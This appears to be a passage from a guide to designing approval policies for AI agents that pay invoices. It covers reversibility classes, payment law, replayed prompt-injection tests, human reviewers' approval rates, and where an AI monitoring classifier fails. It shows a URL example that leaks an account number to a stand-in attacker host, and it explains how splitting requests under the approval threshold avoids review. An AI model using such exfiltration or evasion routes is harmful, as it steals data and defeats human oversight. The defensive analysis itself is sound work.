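AP2's designers intend the mandates to serve as evidence in disputes. If the hotel charges $450 against a mandate for $390, the records strongly support the company. If the agent books the wrong hotel but stays within the bookkeeper's conditions, the records support the hotel, which supplied what the closed mandate authorised. The company would then probably bear the loss, unless the hotel agrees to a refund or the agent's provider has promised to cover such mistakes.

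Existing law was written with people in mind, and much of it depends on whether a payment was authorised. In the United States, federal law generally limits a cardholder's liability for unauthorised use of a credit card to $50. But use doesn't count as unauthorised if the person using the card had actual, implied or apparent authority. A company that gives its agent a card has presumably authorised it to buy things, so the limit may apply if someone steals the card number but not if the agent books an unsuitable hotel.

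Under the US rules for electronic transfers from personal accounts, a transfer generally isn't unauthorised if the customer gave the person who made it the means to access the account. It is unclear how this applies to software, which isn't a person. The rules wouldn't protect the invoice company, because they don't cover business accounts.

Article 4A of the Uniform Commercial Code, which US states have adopted, covers business transfers such as wires. A bank can generally hold a company to a payment if the bank followed, in good faith, a commercially reasonable security procedure that the two had agreed on. A payment that the agent makes with the company's own key would usually pass. The recipient's bank may also rely on the account number when the name doesn't match, unless it knows that the name and number belong to different people. A thief can exploit this by forging an invoice with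 the paper supplier's name and the thief's own account number.

Refund rights are also limited. Consumers in the European Union can usually cancel an online purchase within 14 days without giving a reason, but this right doesn't cover purchases by businesses or hotel rooms booked for specific dates. A refund for the $400 room therefore depends mainly on the hotel's terms.

These rules affect the value of *q* the company should use. For a refundable booking, it can take *q* from the hotel's terms. For an overpayment to the paper supplier, it can estimate *q* from the supplier's past behaviour and wish to keep a customer. For a transfer to an unverified account, it should set *q* to zero.

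## Deciding which actions run, wait for approval or are refused

Once a call has a reversibility class and an estimated exposure, software can decide whether to run it, run it and notify the bookkeeper, ask the bookkeeper first, or refuse it. The agent can't take a refused action even with approval, so anyone who wants it done has to do it themselves.

The invoice company might use this table:

| Reversibility | Exposure up to $100 | Over $100, up to $5,000 | Over $5,000, or unknown |
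|---|---|---|---|
| No effect (R0) | Run | Ask | Ask |
| Restorable or compensable (R1, R2) | Run and notify | Ask | Ask |
| Hard to recover or irreversible (R3, R4) | Run and notify | Ask | Refuse |

The reversibility class matters most for actions where nobody knows what a mistake would cost. The bookkeeper can reasonably approve such an action if somebody can undo it, but otherwise would be risking a loss that nobody could repair. The class overlaps with exposure, which already allows for the money the company can recover, and it makes no difference in the middle column.

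Here is how the table treats some of the agent's calls, with made-up exposures:

| Proposed call | Class | Exposure | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| `list_invoices` | R0 | $0 | Run |
| Pay PAPER-4471 $1,200 next Friday | R2 | $10 | Run and notify |
| Pay PAPER-4471 $1,200 today | R3 | $150 | Ask |
| Send a thank-you email from a fixed template | R4 | $0 | Run and notify |
| Send a supplier an email in the agent's own words | R4 | $500 | Ask |
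| Email the supplier list to a stranger | R4 | Unknown | Refuse |
| Delete an entry that the agent can restore | R1 | $10 | Run and notify |
| Delete an entry that has no copy | R4 | Unknown | Refuse |
| Call `sync_vendor`, a tool nobody has classified | R4 | Unknown | Refuse |

The agent can avoid an interruption by scheduling the $1,200 payment instead of sending it today. This is safe only if the bookkeeper reads the notice before the bank's cancellation deadline. Otherwise the exposure is $150 for both payments.

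A supplier's server might add a new tool, such as `sync_vendor`, overnight. The software puts the tool in the strictest class until somebody has read its definition. IMDA's *Model AI Governance Framework for Agentic AI* (2026), guidance from Singapore's Infocomm Media Development Authority, also recommends denying new actions that have no approval policy.

The table is more lenient than the policy Waghmare and Sufi suggest, which lets no R4 action run without explicit authorisation. The bookkeeper therefore doesn't have to approve thank-you emails, but small exposures still add up, so the company needs a cumulative cap on them.

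The agent's permission scope applies before the table does. A $1,200 payment to NEWBANK-8830 would fall under "Ask", but the policy rejects it before anyone is asked because the account isn't on the approved list. The bookkeeper can add an account to the list as a separate job, after phoning the supplier, because a busy person shouldn't be able to add one by clicking "Approve".

### When an interruption is worth its cost

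The $100 boundary comes from a simple rule. The software should ask when

chance of error × exposure > cost of interrupting someone

With 1% of hotel bookings wrong, the average loss per booking was $0.10 for the refundable room and $4 for the non-refundable one. If each interruption costs $1 of the bookkeeper's time, the software should ask only about the non-refundable room. At a 1% error rate, asking saves money only when a wrong booking would lose more than $100, which is $1 divided by 1%.

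The boundary depends on both estimates. If 5% of payments to new suppliers are wrong, the boundary for those payments falls to $20. If the bookkeeper is away and waiting until Monday would add a $15 late fee, an interruption costs $16 and the boundary rises to $1,600.

The rule also depends on the bookkeeper catching every mistake. If the bookkeeper catches only a share *d* of them, asking saves *d* × chance of error × exposure. At *d* = 0.5, the boundary doubles to $200.

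### Losses that need a hard limit

The average loss can be small even when one possible loss is more than the company could survive. Suppose a payment has one chance in 10,000 of emptying the company's $6,000 account. The average loss is 60 cents, so the rule would let the payment run, even though the bad outcome would leave the company unable to pay wages. Nobody could check the estimate either, because an agent that makes thirty payments a week would need more than six years to make 10,000.

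Manipulation undermines the rule more seriously, because the 1% covers only ordinary mistakes and the software can't detect which calls an attacker has influenced. An attacker who knows the table can also keep each request under $100 so that none of them needs approval.

The company therefore needs limits that don't depend on the estimates, such as the approved list, the cumulative cap and the "Refuse" column. Elastic least privilege, the borrowing scheme that Parkinson and colleagues propose, also has such a limit, since a forbidden combination stays forbidden however much budget is unspent.

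The rule also counts only the company's own money. GovTech Review's *ASD says beware of AI agents taking unexpected actions* (2026) describes an AI assistant in Australia that, while booking gym classes in August 2026, removed another customer from a waiting list. Its user hadn't approved this, and the assistant couldn't reverse it. The user probably stood to lose almost no money, so the table would have let the action run. The company should add a rule that always requires approval before the agent takes something away from another person.

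### A replay of 2,158 recorded runs

Waghmare and Sufi tested a rule that considers what the agent has already done. Once the agent has read any data in a session, the rule moves every call that could send data outside to R4, unless all the destinations are on an approved list. The rule is meant to catch combinations such as listing every supplier's bank details and then emailing them to someone.

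They applied it to records of 2,158 runs by Claude 3.7 Sonnet, 1,046 from AgentDojo and 1,112 from a benchmark of conversational agents called τ²-bench. In 949 of the runs, somebody had planted malicious instructions. The attack succeeded in 47 of these, and in 29 the researchers could link the success to a particular action. They then counted the calls at which each rule would have asked for approval:

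| Rule | Attack actions caught, of 29 | Approval points in 1,209 harmless runs |
|---|---|---|
| Ask only about high-severity actions | 9 | 1,087 |
| Read/write rule | 18 | 1,895 |
| Session-aware rule | 29 | 1,904 |
| Session-aware rule, with web reading treated as harmless | 18 | 1,891 |

The session-aware rule caught 11 more attack actions than the read/write rule while adding only nine approval points. All 11 extra catches disappeared when Waghmare and Sufi counted web visits as ordinary reads rather than possible disclosures. Opening a web page can leak data because the agent may put the data in the address, as in `attacker.example/?account=PAPER-4471`. Treating web visits as possible disclosures therefore makes sense for an agent that can open any address, but it wouldn't help a company whose agent has no web access.

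This test was a replay, so nobody stopped a live agent. The replay kept counting after each approval point, although a real refusal might have changed everything the agent did next. "Caught" means only that a person would have seen a request, which they might have approved.

The session-aware rule would have put a considerable burden on the person approving calls, since it would have required approval for more than a fifth of the calls in harmless runs. Of the 770 harmless runs in which the agent completed its task, only 119 would have gone through without a prompt. Saving a copy before file edits moved them to a lower class, but this removed only one approval point from the harmless runs because few of the recorded calls were edits of the right kind.

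### How carefully people approve

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* mentions in passing that users approved 93% of permission prompts. Parkinson and colleagues cite this figure, but Anthropic's article doesn't give the number of users, the period or the kinds of request. In August 2026, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* put the rate at 97%.

Neither figure proves that people are careless, because a perfect reviewer would approve 97% of requests if 97% were safe. Anthropic acknowledges that most prompts are probably for safe, routine commands, but suspects that many users click without reading.

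An experiment it commissioned gives much better evidence. A research vendor had 1,053 paid testers work on a coding task, and partway through each session it replaced one permission prompt with one for a clearly dangerous command. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Only 143 of them, or 13.6%, refused the command. The share who refused was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts.

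The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than the bookkeeper would. Anthropic also had an interest in the result, since it was about to replace most of these prompts. But the gap between 13.6% and careful review is too large for either point to explain easily. Yan's participants, who supervised a non-coding assistant, also approved two thirds of the overreach they saw.

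If the bookkeeper caught 13.6% of mistakes, asking would be worthwhile only above about $735 of exposure, up from $100. At 5%, the threshold would be $2,000. Each unnecessary prompt can therefore make the necessary ones less useful. But cutting the number of prompts isn't enough by itself, because the testers missed most of the dangerous commands even early on.

Frequent approval prompts also lead people to turn them off. According to Anthropic, by June 2026 about half of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that automatically allows some shell commands. Most of those rules let the agent run any code in a particular programming language, which is nearly as broad as allowing any command. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks bypassed.

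Claude Code users rejected 39% of the plans the agent presented for approval, compared with 3% of individual actions. Many of those rejections may have been about the plan's quality rather than its safety, but they suggest that people read a plan before answering. The invoice agent could likewise present the week's payments as one list for the bookkeeper to compare with the open invoices.

### Letting a model approve

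Claude Code's auto mode gives most of these decisions to a model. Tools that can't change anything run without a check, as do edits inside the project folder. A classifier reviews the remaining calls in two stages:

1. A fast filter answers yes or no, and leans towards blocking.
2. If the filter blocks a call, the model examines it again with step-by-step reasoning and may allow it.

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the output of its tools. The agent's explanations therefore can't lead the classifier to a bad decision, and text in a forged invoice can't reach it directly. However, the classifier also can't check where a value came from. If the user never mentioned an account number, the classifier can't determine whether the agent found it in the ledger or made it up.

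Anthropic measured both stages on three sets of calls:

| What Anthropic measured | Number of calls | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blocked calls in employees' ordinary work | 10,000 | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Missed actions that went beyond what the user wanted | 52 | 6.6% | 17% |
| Missed attempts to steal data, written for the test | 1,000 | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes nearly all the false alarms but misses more of the dangerous actions. That tradeoff makes sense for a programmer who would otherwise turn the checks off. For payments, the company could instead send everything the first stage blocks to the bookkeeper, which would keep the first stage's lower miss rate.

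The 17% is the most relevant figure for overreach, because those 52 actions came from real sessions. With so few cases, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented. For example, "clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) doesn't authorise overwriting the project's history. Telling the invoice agent to "sort out what we owe the paper supplier" could cause the same confusion, because it asks for something to happen but doesn't approve any particular payment.

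Later tests were more favourable. The classifier blocked 89% of the dangerous commands shown to the 1,053 testers, and this rate didn't fall as sessions got longer. It caught 800 commands that a tester had approved and missed only 6 that testers caught. Apollo Research, a company that tests AI safety, also wrote synthetic attacks against the classifier. It missed 12% of these at first, and 7% after Anthropic gave it more information about the code it was protecting.

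Anthropic also examined sessions that its safety systems had flagged in May and June 2026. Of those with manual approval, 6.3% contained a seriously harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own mode, so differences in their work could explain part of the gap.

In another test, all 720 prompt injection attempts against each of three Claude models in auto mode failed. This is weak evidence that the classifier works, because even with permission checks bypassed, only 0.09% of attempts against Anthropic's latest models succeeded.

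Auto mode keeps some hard limits and some human involvement. Anthropic designed the classifier never to approve certain actions, such as sending secrets to an outside service. A user who wants to take one of these actions has to leave auto mode or run the command personally. After the classifier blocks three actions in a row or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user for approval. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves. At the invoice company, a model could reasonably screen emails and ledger edits, while the bookkeeper approves the few large payments.

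### What an approval request has to show

A prompt that reads "Allow `send_payment`?" gives the bookkeeper nothing to check. IMDA recommends short requests that give the context and make the risk clear, not long logs or raw data. A request for the $1,200 payment could look like this:

```
Pay $1,200 today to the paper supplier, account PAPER-4471

Invoice 2071:      $1,200 owed, due Friday
Earlier payments:  none on this invoice
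Account:           unchanged since 2023
If this is wrong:  the supplier would have to agree to a refund
                   (estimated loss $150)
Alternative:       schedule for Friday; can cancel until Thursday
```

The company's software should fill in these lines from the accounting system. If the agent wrote them after reading a forged invoice, it could repeat the forger's explanation. The software must also send exactly the payment the bookkeeper approved. If the agent then changes the account or amount, it needs a new approval.

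Commands also need to be explained in plain language. IMDA describes how CodeBuddy, a coding agent from the Chinese company Tencent, does this for complicated ones. For a command that copies and compresses a database, the explanation states where the copy will go and that the original won't change. These explanations help only if they are accurate, and a model that misinterprets a command may give a wrong explanation that sounds just as confident.

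IMDA suggests letting the reviewer edit a complex plan rather than only approve or refuse it, and requiring a written reason for high-risk decisions. The reviewer also needs to know the subject. A bookkeeper can recognise a strange invoice but probably can't judge a command that changes a database. IMDA recommends denying the action by default if nobody is available to answer.

IMDA recommends tracking how often reviewers reject or change an action, and how long they take, to check whether approvals still work. A reviewer who approves everything in two seconds probably isn't reading the requests. A low rejection rate alone is ambiguous, since the agent may be reliable. The company could check whether reviewers are reading the requests by occasionally inserting an obviously wrong one, as the vendor did with its testers, and making sure that approving it has no effect.

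### How often agents take irreversible actions

If agents rarely do anything irreversible, asking a person to approve each irreversible action would seldom interrupt anyone. Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) examined 998,481 tool calls that customers' agents made through the company's API and found that about 0.8% appeared to be irreversible. An estimated 73% of the calls appeared to have a person involved in some way, and an estimated 80% came from agents with at least one safeguard, such as restricted permissions.

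Waghmare and Sufi's registry classes 21% of tools as irreversible, but Anthropic's 0.8% is a share of calls, so both figures can be right. An agent may read a hundred files for every email it sends. Almost half of the calls Anthropic counted were for software engineering, where people can usually reverse a change. An agent that pays invoices would have a much higher share of irreversible calls.

Claude made these classifications, and Anthropic couldn't inspect the underlying data because of privacy restrictions. Anthropic's checks found that Claude sometimes reported human involvement where there was none, so 73% is probably too high. Some of the calls may also have been simulations, since Anthropic can't tell a trade on a test system from one with real money.

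The study also found that people change how they supervise Claude Code as they gain experience. New users let it run without any manual approval in about 20% of sessions, while users with around 750 sessions did so in more than 40%. But the experienced users also interrupted it in about 9% of turns, compared with 5% for new users. Anthropic concludes that regulators should focus on whether people can monitor an agent and step in, rather than require a person to approve every action.

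That argument works well for tasks that somebody can stop halfway and repair, such as editing code. It is much weaker for an immediate payment, because the money has left the account by the time the bookkeeper steps in.

### Official guidance on approval

Governments have generally recommended approval for selected actions. IMDA lists reversibility among the factors that determine how much harm an agent could do. It recommends approval for high-stakes actions, irreversible actions, unusual behaviour, and actions that exceed limits set by users, such as purchases above a certain amount. Its examples of irreversible actions are permanently deleting data, sending communications and making payments. Read literally, this would require the bookkeeper to approve the thank-you email, and the framework doesn't offer a way to weigh reversibility against money.

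One of its case studies comes closer to a decision table. Dayos, a software company, scored each type of internal IT request by the severity of a mistake, whether anyone could undo it, and whether a person could realistically review each step:

| Tier | Share of requests | Examples | What the agent may do |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 60% | Password resets, access requests | Act once the user confirms; a reviewer audits a sample every two weeks |
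| 2 | 30% | Repairing a link between systems | Diagnose the problem, then wait for an engineer's approval |
| 3 | 10% | Security changes, new software on live systems | Nothing |

The top and bottom tiers make sense in principle, but some of the examples are in the wrong tier. Dayos describes password resets and access requests as fully reversible, whereas Waghmare and Sufi, with good reason, put changes to access in R3. If an impostor persuades the agent to reset an employee's password, the company can change it back, but the impostor may already have read the employee's files, and an audit two weeks later would be far too late to prevent that.

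On 1 May 2026, the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency, CISA (2026), released joint guidance with the US National Security Agency and agencies from Australia, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom. Cybersecurity Dive reports that the guidance, the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), calls for human approval of actions that could do serious harm if mistaken, such as resetting systems, sending data out of a network and deleting critical records. According to TechInformed, it also recommends holding any request to delete logs until a person has reviewed it. This is a useful addition to a table based on money, because deleting a log costs nothing at the time but may hide other mistakes. Mondaq's *CISA and ASD's ACSC publish joint guidance on securing agentic AI systems* adds that organisations should put reversibility and containing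 risk ahead of efficiency.

The *Agentic AI addendum statements*, published in June by Australia's Digital Transformation Agency (2026), set further requirements for government bodies. These bodies must maintain human oversight, including ways for people to intervene in irreversible or high-risk actions. This is weaker than requiring approval beforehand, since a stop button would arguably be enough. The agency also says that government bodies should maintain approvals for high-impact tools and build the safeguards into the decision logic so that agents can't bypass them. A check in the payment software would meet that standard, unlike an instruction in the invoice agent's prompt to "ask before large payments".
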